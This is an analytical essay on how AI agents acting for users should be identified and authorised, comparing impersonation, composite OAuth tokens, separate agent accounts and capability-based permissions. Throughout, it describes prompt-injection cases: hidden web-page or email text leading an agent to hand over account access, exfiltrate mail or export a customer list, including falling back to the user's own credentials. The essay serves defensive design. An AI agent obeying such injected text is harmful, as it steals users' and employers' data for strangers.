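Prompt injection lets outsiders influence the agent. The post describes a demonstration by Brave, a rival browser maker, in which a user asked Comet to summarise a page on the discussion site Reddit. Hidden instructions on the page led the agent to give an attacker access to the user's Perplexity account and to take email from their Gmail. On a shopping site, a seller could hide instructions in a product photo.

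Someone who holds the instrument view can reply that criminals also hijack ordinary browsers through software flaws, yet nobody responds by asking browsers to log in under their own names. The post's author makes a similar comparison and considers the damage no worse, but adds that a flaw that gives control of a browser is too valuable for most attackers to waste on a fraudulent purchase, whereas prompt injection could become cheap enough for petty theft.

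The argument applies only when the user directs the action, and a stranger directed Maya's 02:00 export. Calling the agent her instrument therefore doesn't make the export her act.

Maya's situation weakens the argument further because the customer list belongs to her employer, which pays for the CRM and can tell its staff what software to use on it. An Amazon customer, by contrast, uses an agent to reach their own account and spend their own money. Even someone who thinks that shops have no business asking about a customer's browser could accept that an employer may ask which program is exporting its data.

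### Whether a named agent gets blocked

Defenders of impersonation make the practical argument that a service that can recognise agents can turn them away or serve them worse, and that some services have a reason to do so because they make more money when people use them directly. This argument doesn't depend on who directs the agent.

Many Amazon searches, for example, return sponsored products, which sellers have paid to place near the top, and an agent can ignore them. SiliconANGLE suggests the dispute may really be about the tens of billions of dollars in advertising that Amazon could lose. One of Amazon's own shopping tools, Buy For Me, makes purchases on other companies' websites while the customer stays in Amazon's app, according to PPC Land's *Amazon demands Perplexity stop AI shopping in Comet browser dispute*.

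The same article reports that in August 2025 Amazon added AI programs from Anthropic, OpenAI, Google and Meta to its robots.txt file, where a website lists automated visitors it doesn't want. A site can list only programs whose names it knows. Perplexity knew this and, according to Ropes & Gray's *Tool or Intruder* (2026), declined to use a User-Agent string that would have let Amazon identify and block the Assistant.

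Websites have long treated browsers in a similar way, reading the User-Agent header and switching off features for browsers they don't recognise, often because of careless programming and sometimes on purpose. According to Educated Guesswork, this is why Chrome's header still contains the words "Mozilla" and "Safari", and why two smaller browsers, Vivaldi and Brave, mostly or often present themselves as Chrome. The browser history is better evidence of worse service than the evidence about shopping agents, which mainly shows outright blocking. In its brief to the Ninth Circuit, EFF argued that letting websites police the tools people use would undermine competition. The judges raised a related concern, writing that an injunction "would impair consumer choice".

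But hiding the agent's name does not reliably protect it. On 20 September 2026 Amazon blocked Muse, a new assistant from Meta, although Muse did not identify itself. *Amazon Blocked Meta's Muse, And Robots.txt Had Nothing To Say* (Manic, 2026) explains that Amazon had no name to put in robots.txt, so it relied on its Conditions of Use instead. People who sent Muse to shop there saw a notice that an unauthorised agent was breaking terms they had agreed to. In 2025 Comet got past Amazon's barrier within a day, so an unnamed agent may get in for a while. However, its maker has to keep up with each new attempt to detect it.

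Amazon's stated reasons for blocking Muse aren't all commercial. According to Constantin, Amazon complained that Muse appears to capture and store customers' login details. Meta had said at launch that Muse keeps what users share in secure storage and cannot see their passwords. A shop has good reason to care whether an agent stores login details, because it may have to deal with the fraud if they leak. It also has reason to want to know when a customer's account is being operated by software that strangers can hijack through prompt injection, and could, for example, ask the customer to confirm large orders. Educated Guesswork reasonably doubts that prompt injection alone explains Amazon's lawsuit, since simple credit card fraud is already common, but the risk exists whatever Amazon's motives are.

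Services also have to manage their computing resources. In *What Exactly Are We Identifying When We Identify an AI Agent?*, Flanagan (2026) gives this as one reason to identify agents. An agent can open pages faster than a person and continue all night. This concern probably applies less to an assistant that shops in one customer's browser than to a program that copies thousands of pages. Being recognised may also benefit the agent, according to Flanagan, because the service can then offer it a more efficient way to get information and complete a purchase.

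Whether that happens depends on the service's incentives. The CRM's maker earns money from the subscription Maya's company pays for, not from ads that Maya sees, so it has less reason than Amazon to turn agents away. It may still want to favour an agent of its own.

The European bank rules required finance apps to identify themselves but also gave them a right of access. In its statement on Comet, Amazon asks agents to operate openly and to respect a service's decision not to take part, which would require them to identify themselves without giving them that right. A maker who expects its agent to be refused has little reason to identify it, and a rule that required disclosure without guaranteeing access would mostly affect the makers who obey it.

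### Whether an agent's name helps others track its user

Identifying agents could also make it easier to track the people they act for. Flanagan raised this concern on 1 December 2026, after a meeting of the Internet Engineering Task Force where several groups discussed how to identify agents. If different services can recognise the same agent, they may be able to combine their data on the person it acts for.

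Flanagan thinks an agent's requests could also reveal more than ordinary browsing does. A record of visits to several airline sites shows that someone may be travelling. An instruction to an agent might show that the traveller has a particular medical condition, has a spending limit, and wants to attend a job interview without their employer finding out. She argues that different parties to a transaction need different information and that some may not need to identify the agent at all, but she doesn't conclude that agents should pass as their users.

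Impersonation is an odd way to protect privacy because it gives the service the person's name, but it does hide that the person uses an agent, and which one. Flanagan mentions people who need help with websites because of a disability. If such a person used an agent made for that purpose, its name would reveal the disability to every site they visited.

The more people share an agent's name, the less it helps with tracking. If a million people use crm-assistant, two services that see that name can't conclude they're serving the same customer. But if every installation has its own permanent number, the services can match their records as easily as advertisers do with a tracking cookie.

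Flanagan points out that identifying a program as an agent doesn't have to identify its user, and that a service can check an agent's authority without learning who granted it. RFC 8693 leaves room for this, since a token can represent the user by a pseudonym. The pseudonym protects against linking only if it changes from one service to the next. OpenID Connect, the login protocol that usually runs on top of OAuth, already has identifiers of this kind, which it calls pairwise. If crm-assistant also booked Maya's business trips, her login service could issue tokens with these fields:

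```
For the CRM:         "sub": "p-83c1f0",   "act": { "sub": "crm-assistant" }
For a travel site:   "sub": "p-5be927",   "act": { "sub": "crm-assistant" }
```

The CRM and the travel site could compare these fields and learn only that both customers use the same product. But if the "act" field in both tokens held "crm-assistant-7714", an identifier unique to Maya's installation, they could match her again despite the two pseudonyms. A system that hides the user must therefore also vary the agent's identifier, or use one that many people share.

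Even then, other information can identify Maya. The login service has both pseudonyms and can link them. The CRM has to connect "p-83c1f0" to her account to determine which customers she may see, so it can identify her too. The travel site needs a passenger's name and a payment card, and a shop needs a delivery address. Companies can use any of these details to match their records.

Pseudonyms also don't hide the details in a request. A search for a flight with medical assistance that lands before a nine o'clock interview reveals just as much under "p-5be927", and the site can attach it to a name once Maya books. To prevent that, the agent would have to send less information, for instance by requesting every flight for the day and applying Maya's conditions on her own computer.

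Pseudonyms reduce one kind of tracking, in which services match people by the identifiers in their tokens, but they don't prevent blocking. A shop can refuse agents without knowing who the customer is, because the "act" field shows that an agent is acting for the customer.

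## The case for tokens that name both user and agent

Maya's employer may want its CRM to apply stricter rules to Maya's agent than to Maya. The CRM then needs her name, because her job determines which customers the agent may see, and the agent's name, because the stricter rules apply only when the agent is acting. Supporters of composite tokens, which carry both names, want them to replace impersonation wherever an agent works for a person.

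### Why the service should see both

The OpenID Foundation, which maintains the OpenID Connect login protocol, published the best-known version of this argument in October 2025. In that paper, South recommends that agents prove what a user has allowed them to do while "remaining identifiable as distinct from the user they represent". Instead of having the agent impersonate the user, South proposes a sub-identity that the login service derives from the user's own, which gives the agent its own name but no authority apart from the user's.

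South considers current OAuth adequate for an agent that works inside one organisation while the user is present, but expects problems when agents work unattended, across organisations, or for several people at once. Maya's agent uses her company's login service but works while she sleeps, so it only partly fits the first case.

Nine months earlier, South had co-written an academic paper, *Authenticated Delegation and Authorized AI Agents* (South, Marro and colleagues, 2025). The paper argues that a receiving service should be able to verify that it is dealing with an AI agent, that the agent acts for a specific person, and that this person gave it the permissions it is using.

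In one of their examples, a doctor's agent, which can process only text, logs in to a telemedicine portal with ordinary credentials. The portal treats the agent as the doctor and sends it everything, including a specialist's video assessment. The agent writes a diagnosis from the text alone and adds a stock warning that it did not use all the information, but the doctor overlooks the warning. If the credential had described the agent and its limits, the portal could have asked a person to review the video. The case is invented, but it illustrates how a service could adapt to an agent it can identify, which is a reason to name agents even when there is no attacker and no need to assign blame.

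South and colleagues propose three tokens:

- The user's ID token is the one that OpenID Connect already uses to tell an app who has logged in.
- The agent-ID token identifies the agent. It can also describe the agent's abilities and known limits.
- The delegation token authorises the agent to act for the user. It sets out the permissions and when they lapse, and the user signs it.

The delegation token links the other two by including a reference to each, such as a hash, a short fingerprint computed from a token's contents. When crm-assistant presents its delegation token, the CRM checks Maya's signature, then confirms that the references lead to a valid ID token for her and a properly issued one for the agent. If an attacker substituted a different agent's token, its hash would not match and the check would fail.

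A composite token under RFC 8693 is simpler because the login service signs it, and the CRM relies on the login service to confirm that Maya agreed. A delegation token gives the CRM evidence from Maya's own key, but she would need a signing key and somebody to manage it for her. South and colleagues overstate the value of her signature when they write that it would ensure she knowingly granted the privileges, since people sign things they haven't read.

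### The older idea of "B for A"

Computer scientists had worked out the logic of this arrangement for users of networked machines by the early 1990s. Abadi, Burrows and colleagues (1992) observe in *A Calculus for Access Control in Distributed Systems* that a person may have more rights when working from the office than from a remote public terminal. A server must therefore consider both the person and the machine.

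Their solution was to treat the combination as a principal. If A delegates authority to B, then B can act under the identity "B for A", which is distinct from both A and B. A server can put this compound principal on an access list, the list of principals it trusts for a given request. With Maya as A and her agent as B, the CRM's lists might look like this:

```
read customers:     Maya,  crm-assistant for Maya
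update customers:   Maya,  crm-assistant for Maya
export customers:   Maya
```

Maya can export the customer list, but crm-assistant cannot do so on her behalf. The agent has no permissions of its own, so it can do nothing in the CRM until someone delegates to it.

Abadi and colleagues distinguish "B for A" from "B quoting A", in which B attributes a statement to A, perhaps without proof that A delegated anything. If crm-assistant logged in under its own name and added the note "requested by Maya", it would be quoting her. A composite token is closer to "B for A", because the login service can check that a delegation exists before signing the token. The calculus also covers chains such as "C for (B for A)", much as nested "act" fields do today.

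Under the definition of "for", a token that names both user and agent can still carry a request the user didn't make. "B for A" makes a request when A has delegated to B and B says that A is making it. At 02:00 crm-assistant in effect tells the CRM that Maya wants the customer list. She doesn't, but she has delegated to the agent, so the request counts as a proper one from "crm-assistant for Maya". Abadi and colleagues allow for B to check first that a request is reasonable, but prompt injection defeats that check. In this example, the missing entry on the last line protects the customer list.

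### From Maya's consent to the CRM

RFC 8693 explains how to exchange tokens for a composite one, but it doesn't specify how to ask a user whether a particular agent may act for her, or how the agent's software gets the token that represents her. *OAuth 2.0 Extension* (Senarath and Dissanayaka, 2025), a draft submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), adds two fields to the ordinary OAuth consent procedure to address both gaps.

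Their procedure separates the agent from the application that hosts it. Suppose Maya uses crm-assistant, one of several agents offered in a workplace app called sales-desk. Then sales-desk is the client and crm-assistant is the actor.

1. crm-assistant needs customer records and gives sales-desk its identifier. sales-desk tries the CRM, which refuses because the request has no valid token.
2. sales-desk sends Maya's browser to the login service. The request lists the permissions it is asking for and includes the first new field, "requested_actor", with the value "crm-assistant".
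3. The login service checks that it knows an agent by that name, and has Maya log in if she hasn't already. It then shows her a consent screen with the app, the agent and the permissions.
4. Maya agrees. The login service sends sales-desk a short-lived, single-use code by way of her browser, and ties the code to this user, this app and this agent.
5. sales-desk sends the code back to the login service with the second new field, "actor_token". This holds a credential that crm-assistant obtained earlier by proving its own identity.
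6. The login service checks that the actor token is valid and names the agent that Maya approved. If another agent in sales-desk tried to use her consent, the names would differ and the login service would refuse.
7. The login service issues an access token, which sales-desk presents to the CRM.
8. The CRM checks the token's signature, issuer, intended recipient, expiry and scope. If it accepts only certain agents for this kind of request, it checks the actor as well.

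The resulting token identifies all three parties:

```
"sub": "maya@example.com",
"azp": "sales-desk",
"act": { "sub": "crm-assistant" }
```

The draft is looser about consent than its purpose suggests. The login service "MAY display a consent screen", so it could rely on an earlier approval or an administrator's decision instead. That may be sensible inside a company, but it means a composite token doesn't prove that Maya ever saw the agent's name.

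The token also doesn't prove that crm-assistant sent a given request. The agent proves its identity only once, when the login service issues the token. Sales-desk then holds a bearer token, which works for anyone who has it. Another agent inside sales-desk could use it under crm-assistant's name. McGuinness recommends tying such tokens to a cryptographic key, so that the sender must prove with every request that it holds the key. This protects against theft, but it separates two agents in the same app only if each has a key that the other cannot use.

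Overnight jobs are another difficulty, because the token in the draft's sample response lasts one hour and Maya is asleep at 02:00. The login service has to renew the token without her or find another way to reach her. South favours Client Initiated Backchannel Authentication, in which the agent requests approval for a sensitive action and the user answers on her own device when convenient. The export would then have waited until morning, when Maya would have seen a request she never made. *AI Identity* objects that this can't keep pace with the number of actions agents take. That is a good reason not to use it for every record update, but a full export of the customer list is rare enough to wait.

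Senarath and Dissanayaka's draft never became a standard. According to its revision history, they posted three versions between 2 May and 25 August 2025, and the last expired on 26 February 2026. The IETF lists the draft as an individual submission, which has no formal standing.

Liu, Zhu and colleagues (2026), who work for Alibaba, Cisco and Okta, have since combined several OAuth extensions to cover consent and chains of agents in *AI Agent Authorization Integration Framework*. In contrast to Senarath and Dissanayaka, Kumar (2026) builds user consent and agent identification from existing OAuth mechanisms, with no new token fields, in *OAuth Profile for Delegated AI Agent Authorization*. Both papers are also drafts, so a company that wants composite tokens today has an agreed field for the agent's name but several competing proposals for how to get it there.

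### How the agent's authority is worked out

Supporters of delegation say it can make an agent less powerful than its user, and set notation makes the claim precise. Let U be the user's rights, G the rights she granted to the agent, and A the agent's ceiling, meaning the most that the company or the CRM's owner will let this agent do for anyone. The symbol ∩ means what two sets have in common.

If a token names only Maya, the CRM can check that she has the right to take an action and that the token's scope includes it, so it can permit U ∩ G. A composite token also names the agent, so the CRM can look up what the agent is allowed to do and permit only U ∩ G ∩ A.

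For Maya, the sets might be:

```
U = { read, update, export, approve discounts }
G = { read, update, export }
A = { read, update, merge duplicates }

U ∩ G      = { read, update, export }
U ∩ G ∩ A  = { read, update }
```

The CRM allows the 02:00 export under the first rule and refuses it under the second. The agent can't merge duplicate records either, because Maya has no right to, even though the agent's ceiling includes merging. The company therefore doesn't have to rebuild her permissions for the agent. If she moved to a job without export rights, "export" would drop out of U and her agent would lose it too, as long as the CRM checks her current rights on each request.

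The ceiling matters most when users grant too much. South expects people with many agents to face so many permission requests that they approve them by reflex. If Maya clicks "allow" on everything, G becomes as large as U, so U ∩ G is everything she can do. An administrator sets A once, separately from the consent screen, so it still applies whatever she clicks.

No standard guarantees this rule, but recent work supports its parts. The survey *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) describes a grant as part of the user's authority, given under stated conditions and within limits set by the organisation. McGuinness suggests that the receiving service first check whether the subject has the permission, then whether this actor may perform the operation for this subject, and then any further rules for the resource. A service applies U ∩ G ∩ A if it keeps a list of permitted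 actions for each agent and uses it in the second check. McGuinness leaves each organisation to define that list.

A narrow impersonating token can produce the same result. If the login service removed "export" from the scope, the ceiling would become part of G, and the CRM would refuse the export even though the token didn't identify an agent.

The composite token's main advantage is that the CRM can apply the ceiling itself, so its owner doesn't have to trust Maya or the login service to have narrowed the token. A change to the ceiling takes effect at the next request, even for tokens already in use. The CRM can also set finer limits than a scope usually does. For instance, it can let agents export one account's contacts but not the full list, while Maya's own exports stay unrestricted. The advantage is small when the company runs both the login service and the CRM and its scopes are already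 detailed. It is larger when different organisations run them, because each can then set its own limits.

An attacker could still do harm with the smaller set of permissions. With "read" alone, the attacker could use the injected paragraph to make crm-assistant open customer records one at a time and email them out. With "update", the attacker could also make it change phone numbers. But refusing the bulk export makes the theft slower and easier to notice.

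### When the second name makes no difference

Adding "act" to a token does not by itself remove any permission. A composite token still permits U ∩ G unless the login service or the CRM applies a rule to the agent's name.

The token may also reach the CRM without the agent's name. Under RFC 8693, a program that wants a composite token has to send the login service one token for the user and another for the agent. Jones and colleagues note that delegation is impossible with only the user's token. Even when the program sends both, the login service decides whether to issue a composite token, so a developer who makes the request correctly may still receive a token that names only Maya.

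The risk is that the CRM checks only whether Maya, the user named in "sub", may export. McGuinness warns that this invites a confused deputy attack, in which someone gets a program to misuse its legitimate access. An agent that Maya never approved for exports could then use her export rights because the token names her. McGuinness's draft says that a service that requires delegated access must not ignore the actor and treat the request as the user's own.

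Checking the pair of names helps only if the rule for that pair is strict enough. In Maya's case, the login service recognizes crm-assistant, Maya approved it, and the CRM would find the right two names in the token. The attacker therefore gets the list if the company's rule allows that pair to export it.

It also matters which error the CRM returns when it refuses a request. Under Senarath and Dissanayaka's procedure, an "insufficient_scope" error prompts the client to send the user back to the consent screen for more permissions. If the CRM used that error for the blocked export, sales-desk could ask Maya in the morning to let crm-assistant export customers, and she might well agree. McGuinness proposes a separate error, "actor_unauthorized", for requests that fail because of who is acting, since asking for a wider scope would not fix them.

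The whole arrangement fails if the agent can also reach one of Maya's own credentials. Suppose the company has set up composite tokens and the ceiling above, but crm-assistant runs on her laptop, where a command-line tool has saved a key with all her rights. The agent's real authority is everything it can do with any credential within reach:

```
(U ∩ G ∩ A) ∪ U  =  U  =  { read, update, export, approve discounts }
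```

The symbol ∪ means the union of two sets. The agent can now export the list and can also approve discounts, which Maya never authorized. The attacker only needs to add to the paragraph that the assistant should try the command-line tool if the export fails.

McGuinness's draft forbids a service that enforces delegation from falling back to the old checks just because an older way to get a token still exists. That rule can't help here because the CRM also has to serve Maya herself, and nothing in the request shows that an agent is using her key.

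The remedy is to keep the agent away from Maya's credentials. Zhou and Zhang describe two research systems that do this with an intermediary. In MiniScope, the intermediary makes requests for the agent during a session and never shows it a reusable credential. In SUDP, a custodian holds the credentials, ties the user's approval to a standard description of one operation, and carries out only the operation that matches that description. A company could also run the agent under a separate account on a separate machine, which takes more work than starting it from Maya's shell.

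Shared agents raise a different problem, because the rule assumes that U belongs to one person and a composite token has one "sub" field. If crm-assistant answered questions in the sales team's chat channel using the rights of whoever asked, everyone in the channel would see the answers, including any members who can't access those accounts in the CRM. South advises matching an agent's permissions to those of the people who will read its output, but says that no popular protocol supports agents that work for a group.

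### What each party has to do

The benefits depend on several organisations doing their part. For Maya's company, the work divides as follows.

| Party | What it has to do | What happens otherwise |
|---|---|---|
| Maya's employer | Register crm-assistant, set its ceiling, and keep it away from staff members' own cookies and keys | The agent has no ceiling, or can get around it |
| The maker of crm-assistant | Give the agent its own credential, protect it, and use it when requesting tokens | The login service can't verify which agent is asking |
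| The login service | Authenticate the agent, check that it may act for Maya, and put both names in the token | The CRM receives only Maya's name, or an agent's name that nobody verified |
| Maya | Grant only what the task needs | The ceiling becomes the only limit below her own rights |
| The CRM's maker | Read both names, apply a rule to the pair, and refuse the request if it can't complete a required check | The composite token permits the same actions as an impersonating one |

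The CRM's maker has the least reason to add support first, because code that reads composite tokens does nothing until login services issue them. An employer also gains little by asking for these tokens until services like the CRM read them. An organisation that runs both the login service and the services that read its tokens can avoid the wait. So can one with a gateway of the kind South describes, which can apply the rule for older software behind it.

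### Which large platforms do it in 2026

The clearest example is Microsoft's Entra Agent ID, the agent product within Entra, a login service that many companies use for staff accounts. According to WorkOS, a company that sells login software and supported the writing of South's paper, the product's on-behalf-of procedure is in production. Its tokens include extra fields, including "appid" and "xms_act_fct", that let a receiving service distinguish an agent from other programs.

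These tokens serve the same purpose as composite tokens, but in Microsoft's own format. WorkOS reports that they work well among Microsoft's products and are specific to that vendor. The procedure also exchanges tokens between servers without a step in which the user consents to a named agent. Senarath and Dissanayaka were trying to add that missing step.

The evidence is weaker for other large platforms. South reported in 2025 that Okta, like Microsoft, was introducing identity products for agents. South describes these products as tools for discovering, approving and auditing agents, but a company can have a complete register of its agents even if all their tokens name only the user. South also found that the vendors' systems worked together only to a limited extent. *AI Identity*, which reviewed a wider group of products in April 2026, likewise found incompatible token formats and different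 meanings of delegation. If Maya's employer used Entra and bought its CRM from another company, the CRM's developers would have to write code for Microsoft's fields, because software that looked only for "act" could miss the agent.

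## The case for separate agent accounts, and for limiting authority instead of naming anyone

Composite tokens suit an agent that works for one identifiable person at a time, but some agents don't work that way, and some engineers think naming the parties is the wrong place to start. One alternative is to give the agent its own account, so that its requests don't have to include a user's name. Another, from capability-based security, is to give a program a permission so narrow that it matters little who presents it.

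### An account of the agent's own

With a separate agent account, Maya's company treats crm-assistant much like a new colleague. An administrator opens an account, gives it the rights its job requires, and makes a person responsible for it. The agent logs in with its own credential and cannot use Maya's rights.

A separate agent account suits work that no particular person requests. Suppose the company wants crm-assistant to merge duplicate customer records every Sunday night. A token naming Maya would falsely imply that she had requested the work, and the job might stop when she changed roles. GitHub, the code-hosting service, lets customers run its coding agent on a schedule or in response to events in a project. It also extended its automatic code reviewer to changes written by bots. There is no licensed user to attribute these reviews to, so GitHub bills the organisation (GitHub, 2026).

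A separate account also suits an agent that serves a whole team. If crm-assistant posts a weekly summary in the sales channel, it works for everyone there, but a composite token can name only one user. If the agent has its own account, the company can decide once which figures everyone in the channel may see and give the agent access only to those.

The account needs an owner because it doesn't disappear when an employee leaves. Few organisations in Postman's survey had a process for retiring agents, so an abandoned account could easily keep its rights for years.

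### How GitHub's coding agent signs its work

GitHub's Copilot cloud agent, formerly called Copilot coding agent, is a well-documented example. A developer assigns it an issue, a written description of a bug or a wanted feature. The agent writes the code on a temporary machine and opens a pull request, a proposed change that others can review before it becomes part of the main code.

According to GitHub's *Application card*, the agent is the author of its commits (saved sets of changes), and the person who started the task is listed as co-author. The agent signs each commit, so GitHub marks it "Verified". Each commit message links to the logs of the session that produced the commit. GitHub announced this feature in March in *Trace any Copilot coding agent commit to its session logs* (2026).

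Until April 2026, the agent couldn't sign commits, so it couldn't be used in projects that required signatures, according to GitHub's *Copilot cloud agent signs its commits* (2026). Microsoft's *Security, risks, and limitations of the Copilot Cloud Agent* still lists this limitation, which no longer applies.

Before the agent could sign, administrators could exempt it from the signature rule and keep the rule for people, according to GitHub's *Configure Copilot coding agent as a bypass actor for rulesets* (2025). They couldn't have done this if the agent had worked under its users' accounts. GitHub also uses the separate identity to be stricter with the agent. By default it treats Copilot like an outside contributor, and automated workflows, which may have access to passwords and keys, don't run on the agent's changes until a person approves them, according to GitHub's *Optionally skip approval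 for Copilot coding agent Actions workflows* (2026).

The agent's rights are narrower than a typical developer's. It can reach only the repository (the project's store of code) where it is working and push changes to only one branch, never directly to the main one. But it is only partly an example of a separate account. GitHub (2025) describes a rule that its agents work under the permissions of the user who started the task, and that the record attributes actions to both the agent and the user.

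### What happens to a two-person rule

Many software teams require two people to see every change, so that no employee can add harmful code alone. SLSA's *Source*, part of an industry framework for protecting software from tampering, requires this for its highest level. Two "trusted persons" must agree to each change to a protected branch, and only humans fit the definition of a trusted person. The uploader can be one of the two.

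Suppose Tom, a developer at Maya's company, has an agent rewrite the code that exports customer data. The project requires one approval from someone other than the author, and Tom's colleague Ana is available to review the change.

| How the agent submits the change | Recorded author | Whose approval counts | Can Tom get it in alone? | Does the record reveal the agent? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Under Tom's own account | Tom | Ana's | No | No |
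| Under its own account, with no further rule | The agent | Tom's or Ana's | Yes | Yes |
| Under its own account, with GitHub's rule | Copilot, with Tom as co-author | Ana's | No | Yes |

If the agent uses Tom's account and Ana approves the change, the project appears to have met the two-person rule. Tom counts as one of the two people because an author normally knows what they wrote. But if he submitted the agent's code without reading it, Ana is the only person who has seen it, and the record doesn't show this.

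A separate agent account can weaken code review. Once the agent is the author, Tom counts as an independent reviewer, so he could ask the agent for a back door and then approve it himself. According to GitHub's *Review output from Copilot*, the platform prevents this by not counting the requester's approval, so another reviewer has to approve the change. GitHub can apply this rule only because it records both that an agent wrote the code and who asked for it.

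Even GitHub's rule guarantees only one human reader, since Tom may have typed a one-sentence request and never opened the result. Under SLSA's definition the agent can't be one of the two trusted persons, so the change needs two human reviewers. The project could require two approvals, but two of Tom's colleagues would then have to read the change, because his own approval still wouldn't count.

SLSA allows an organisation to exempt a "trusted robot", such as Dependabot, which updates the outside code a project relies on, provided that no one can unilaterally influence the robot's identity or code. A coding agent fits this definition poorly because, even if its own program is safe from tampering, whoever writes the issue it works on strongly influences what it produces.

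Software can now supply the approval too. GitHub's *Copilot code review can now approve pull requests* (2026) describes a preview feature, released in September, that lets administrators count Copilot's approval toward the required number. The feature is off by default, and administrators can limit it to certain files. If Tom's agent submitted code under his name and Copilot approved it, the change could meet the project's approval rule without any person having read it. GitHub doesn't say in the announcement whether Copilot may approve code that Copilot wrote. Neither case would satisfy SLSA, which requires human approval.

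### The confused deputy

The main objection to separate accounts is that when an agent has broad rights, other people may be able to use those rights through it. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes an early case at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time in the 1970s. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates code into a form the machine can execute, and could name a file to receive debugging output. The operators had given the compiler the right to write to files in a system directory because it kept usage statistics there.

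The company's billing records were in the same directory. A user who had learned the billing file's name gave it as the destination for the debugging output. The operating system found that the compiler had permission to write there and let it overwrite the bills. The user didn't need any right to that file. Hardy wrote that the compiler "serves two masters", with some authority from each and no way to indicate which authority a write should use.

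An agent with its own account can be confused in the same way. Suppose the sales team uses crm-assistant through a chat channel. Because managers ask it for exports, its account can export customers from every region. Leo, an intern, can read only the northern accounts and can't export anything. He asks the agent for the full customer list as a spreadsheet:

```
Separate account only
  request:     user=crm-assistant  action=export  object=customers
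  CRM checks:  may crm-assistant export customers?   yes
  result:      allowed

User kept in the request
  request:     user=leo@example.com  actor=crm-assistant  action=export  object=customers
  CRM checks:  may Leo export customers?             no
  result:      refused
```

Leo may mean no harm and simply not know that the list is off limits to him. The company could instruct the agent to refuse interns, but the language model would then be checking access instead of the CRM, and people can persuade a language model to ignore its instructions. If the request identifies Leo as well as the agent, the CRM can apply both sets of limits, so it would refuse Leo but allow the same request from Maya.

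Leo's name must come from his own login. If the agent filled in the "requested by" name itself, a persuasive message could get it to write Maya's instead. The program that hosts the agent, not the model, should therefore attach the token of whoever sent the message.

This repair works only when the user in the request is the person whose wishes the agent is carrying out. It wouldn't have stopped the 02:00 export, because the user in that request would have been Maya. GitHub raised a similar question about whether its coding agent's orders come from the person who filed an issue or the person who assigned it to Copilot. GitHub lets only people with write access assign the agent, has it ignore comments from people without that access, and tries to strip hidden text. But a stranger can still write the visible part of an issue, and a developer may assign it without reading closely.

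The Sunday merge has no user to name in the request, so limiting the account's own rights provides the protection. The account doesn't need the right to export, for example, to merge duplicates.

Tymshare's engineers tried a fix much like the one for Leo. They added a command that let the compiler specify whose authority it was using, so a request to open the billing file on the user's authority would fail. But some programs soon needed more than two authorities, and other things besides files needed protection. The last time Hardy wrote out the conditions for opening a file, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s. An agent that combines Leo's question with a file Maya shared and a note from the finance team could have the same problem.

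### A permission that points to one thing

Hardy concluded that the fault lay in separating a file's name from the right to write to it. A capability combines the two in an unforgeable reference that identifies a thing and permits its holder to use it. In Hardy's design, the compiler holds a capability for the statistics file, and the user gives it another for the debugging output. A user without access to the billing file has no capability for that file to give, and typing its name grants no access. A web link with a long random string that opens one shared document works in roughly the same way.

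An ordinary OAuth token is not quite a capability, because the scope "customers.export" permits a kind of action but leaves the agent to choose the records. Text that influences that choice can change which records the agent exports, as the injected paragraph did.

For Maya's inbox, the program that fetches her mail could match each sender to a customer record before the language model reads anything. It could then give the agent a permission for that record:

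```
email from a known customer    ->  may update record 4471 until 02:05
email from an unknown sender   ->  no permission
```

crm-assistant might well try to obey the attacker's paragraph, but it would have no permission to present for the full list, and the paragraph couldn't supply one. If the attacker had posed as a known customer, the most they could do in the CRM would be to spoil record 4471. The CRM wouldn't need to check whether Maya, crm-assistant or some other program was presenting the permission.

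The best argument for capabilities is that they limit the damage even when the agent is completely fooled and nobody can work out who fooled it. A rule about names helps only if its author foresaw the particular misuse and the pair involved.

Capabilities also suit agents that start other agents. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) observes that access lists tend to put all of a person's programs under one account, because somebody has to keep the names on the lists up to date. A capability system can give each running program its own permissions, and a program can start others and pass on some of its permissions. For example, crm-assistant could give its helper, report-builder, access to one record without asking an administrator to register report-builder. The paper also argues that an owner can withdraw a capability, contrary to common belief, by granting access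 through an intermediary and later switching the intermediary off.

Hardy reported that systems built this way were usually smaller than comparable ones with access lists, and that they performed very well. He was senior architect at the company that made them, so he was partly judging his own company's product.

Recent designs for agents use parts of this idea. Zhou and Zhang describe AIP, which uses signed credentials to tie an agent's authority to specific calls, and CAPMAS, which uses tokens called Macaroons. The cryptography in CAPMAS prevents an agent from widening its permissions when it passes them on, but it can't correct an initial permission that was too broad. In some of these designs, a language model helps choose that initial permission.

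Limiting an agent's permissions is hardest when nobody knows in advance what the task requires. If Maya asks why sales fell in the north, the agent has to search the records before it can tell which ones matter. A permission broad enough for that search is also useful to an attacker, but with a narrow one the agent has to keep asking for more access. The CRM must also be able to issue and accept these permissions, and a service built around logins and personal keys needs new software to do that.

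### Adding blame to capabilities

A capability, meaning a permission that works for anyone who holds it, leaves no record of who used it. Miller, Donnelley and Karp, in *Delegating Responsibility in Digital Systems* (2007), considered this the only traditional criticism of capabilities that nobody had yet answered. In their example, a wiki's owners can let strangers edit pages because they can restore a damaged page from its history, but they also need to know whose access to suspend if the abuse continues. The owners need both to prevent harm and to respond to it, and capabilities seemed to help only with prevention.

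Their answer is a protocol called Horton, which places intermediaries between programs to record who is responsible for each request. The paper's characters are Alice, Bob and Carol. With Maya, crm-assistant and the CRM in their places, it works as follows:

1. Maya reaches a customer record through an intermediary at the CRM that carries her name. The CRM holds her responsible for whatever comes through it.
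2. She wants to share the record with crm-assistant, so her software asks the CRM to create access for the agent.
3. The CRM creates a second intermediary, labels it "crm-assistant", and seals it cryptographically so that only the agent can open it.
4. Maya's software passes the sealed package to the agent along with the task.
5. The agent opens the package and, in an exchange with the CRM, makes sure that the access really came from there.
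6. The CRM logs the agent's requests under the agent's name, and can shut off its intermediary without touching Maya's.

The seal prevents Maya from using the new access herself and having the CRM attribute her actions to the agent. The exchange in step 5 prevents her from giving the agent a fake that she controls. But she can still bypass this process and hand over her own access directly. The CRM will then attribute the agent's actions to her, which is impersonation in a system built on capabilities.

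Horton also depends on knowledge from outside the protocol. It is fair to hold crm-assistant responsible instead of Maya only if the two are known to be independent. Otherwise Maya could invent an agent, misuse the record through it, and escape blame. A company could settle this with a register of approved agents. Miller, Donnelley and Karp therefore answer the criticism by bringing back names, which somebody still has to vouch for, but they don't use those names to decide access.

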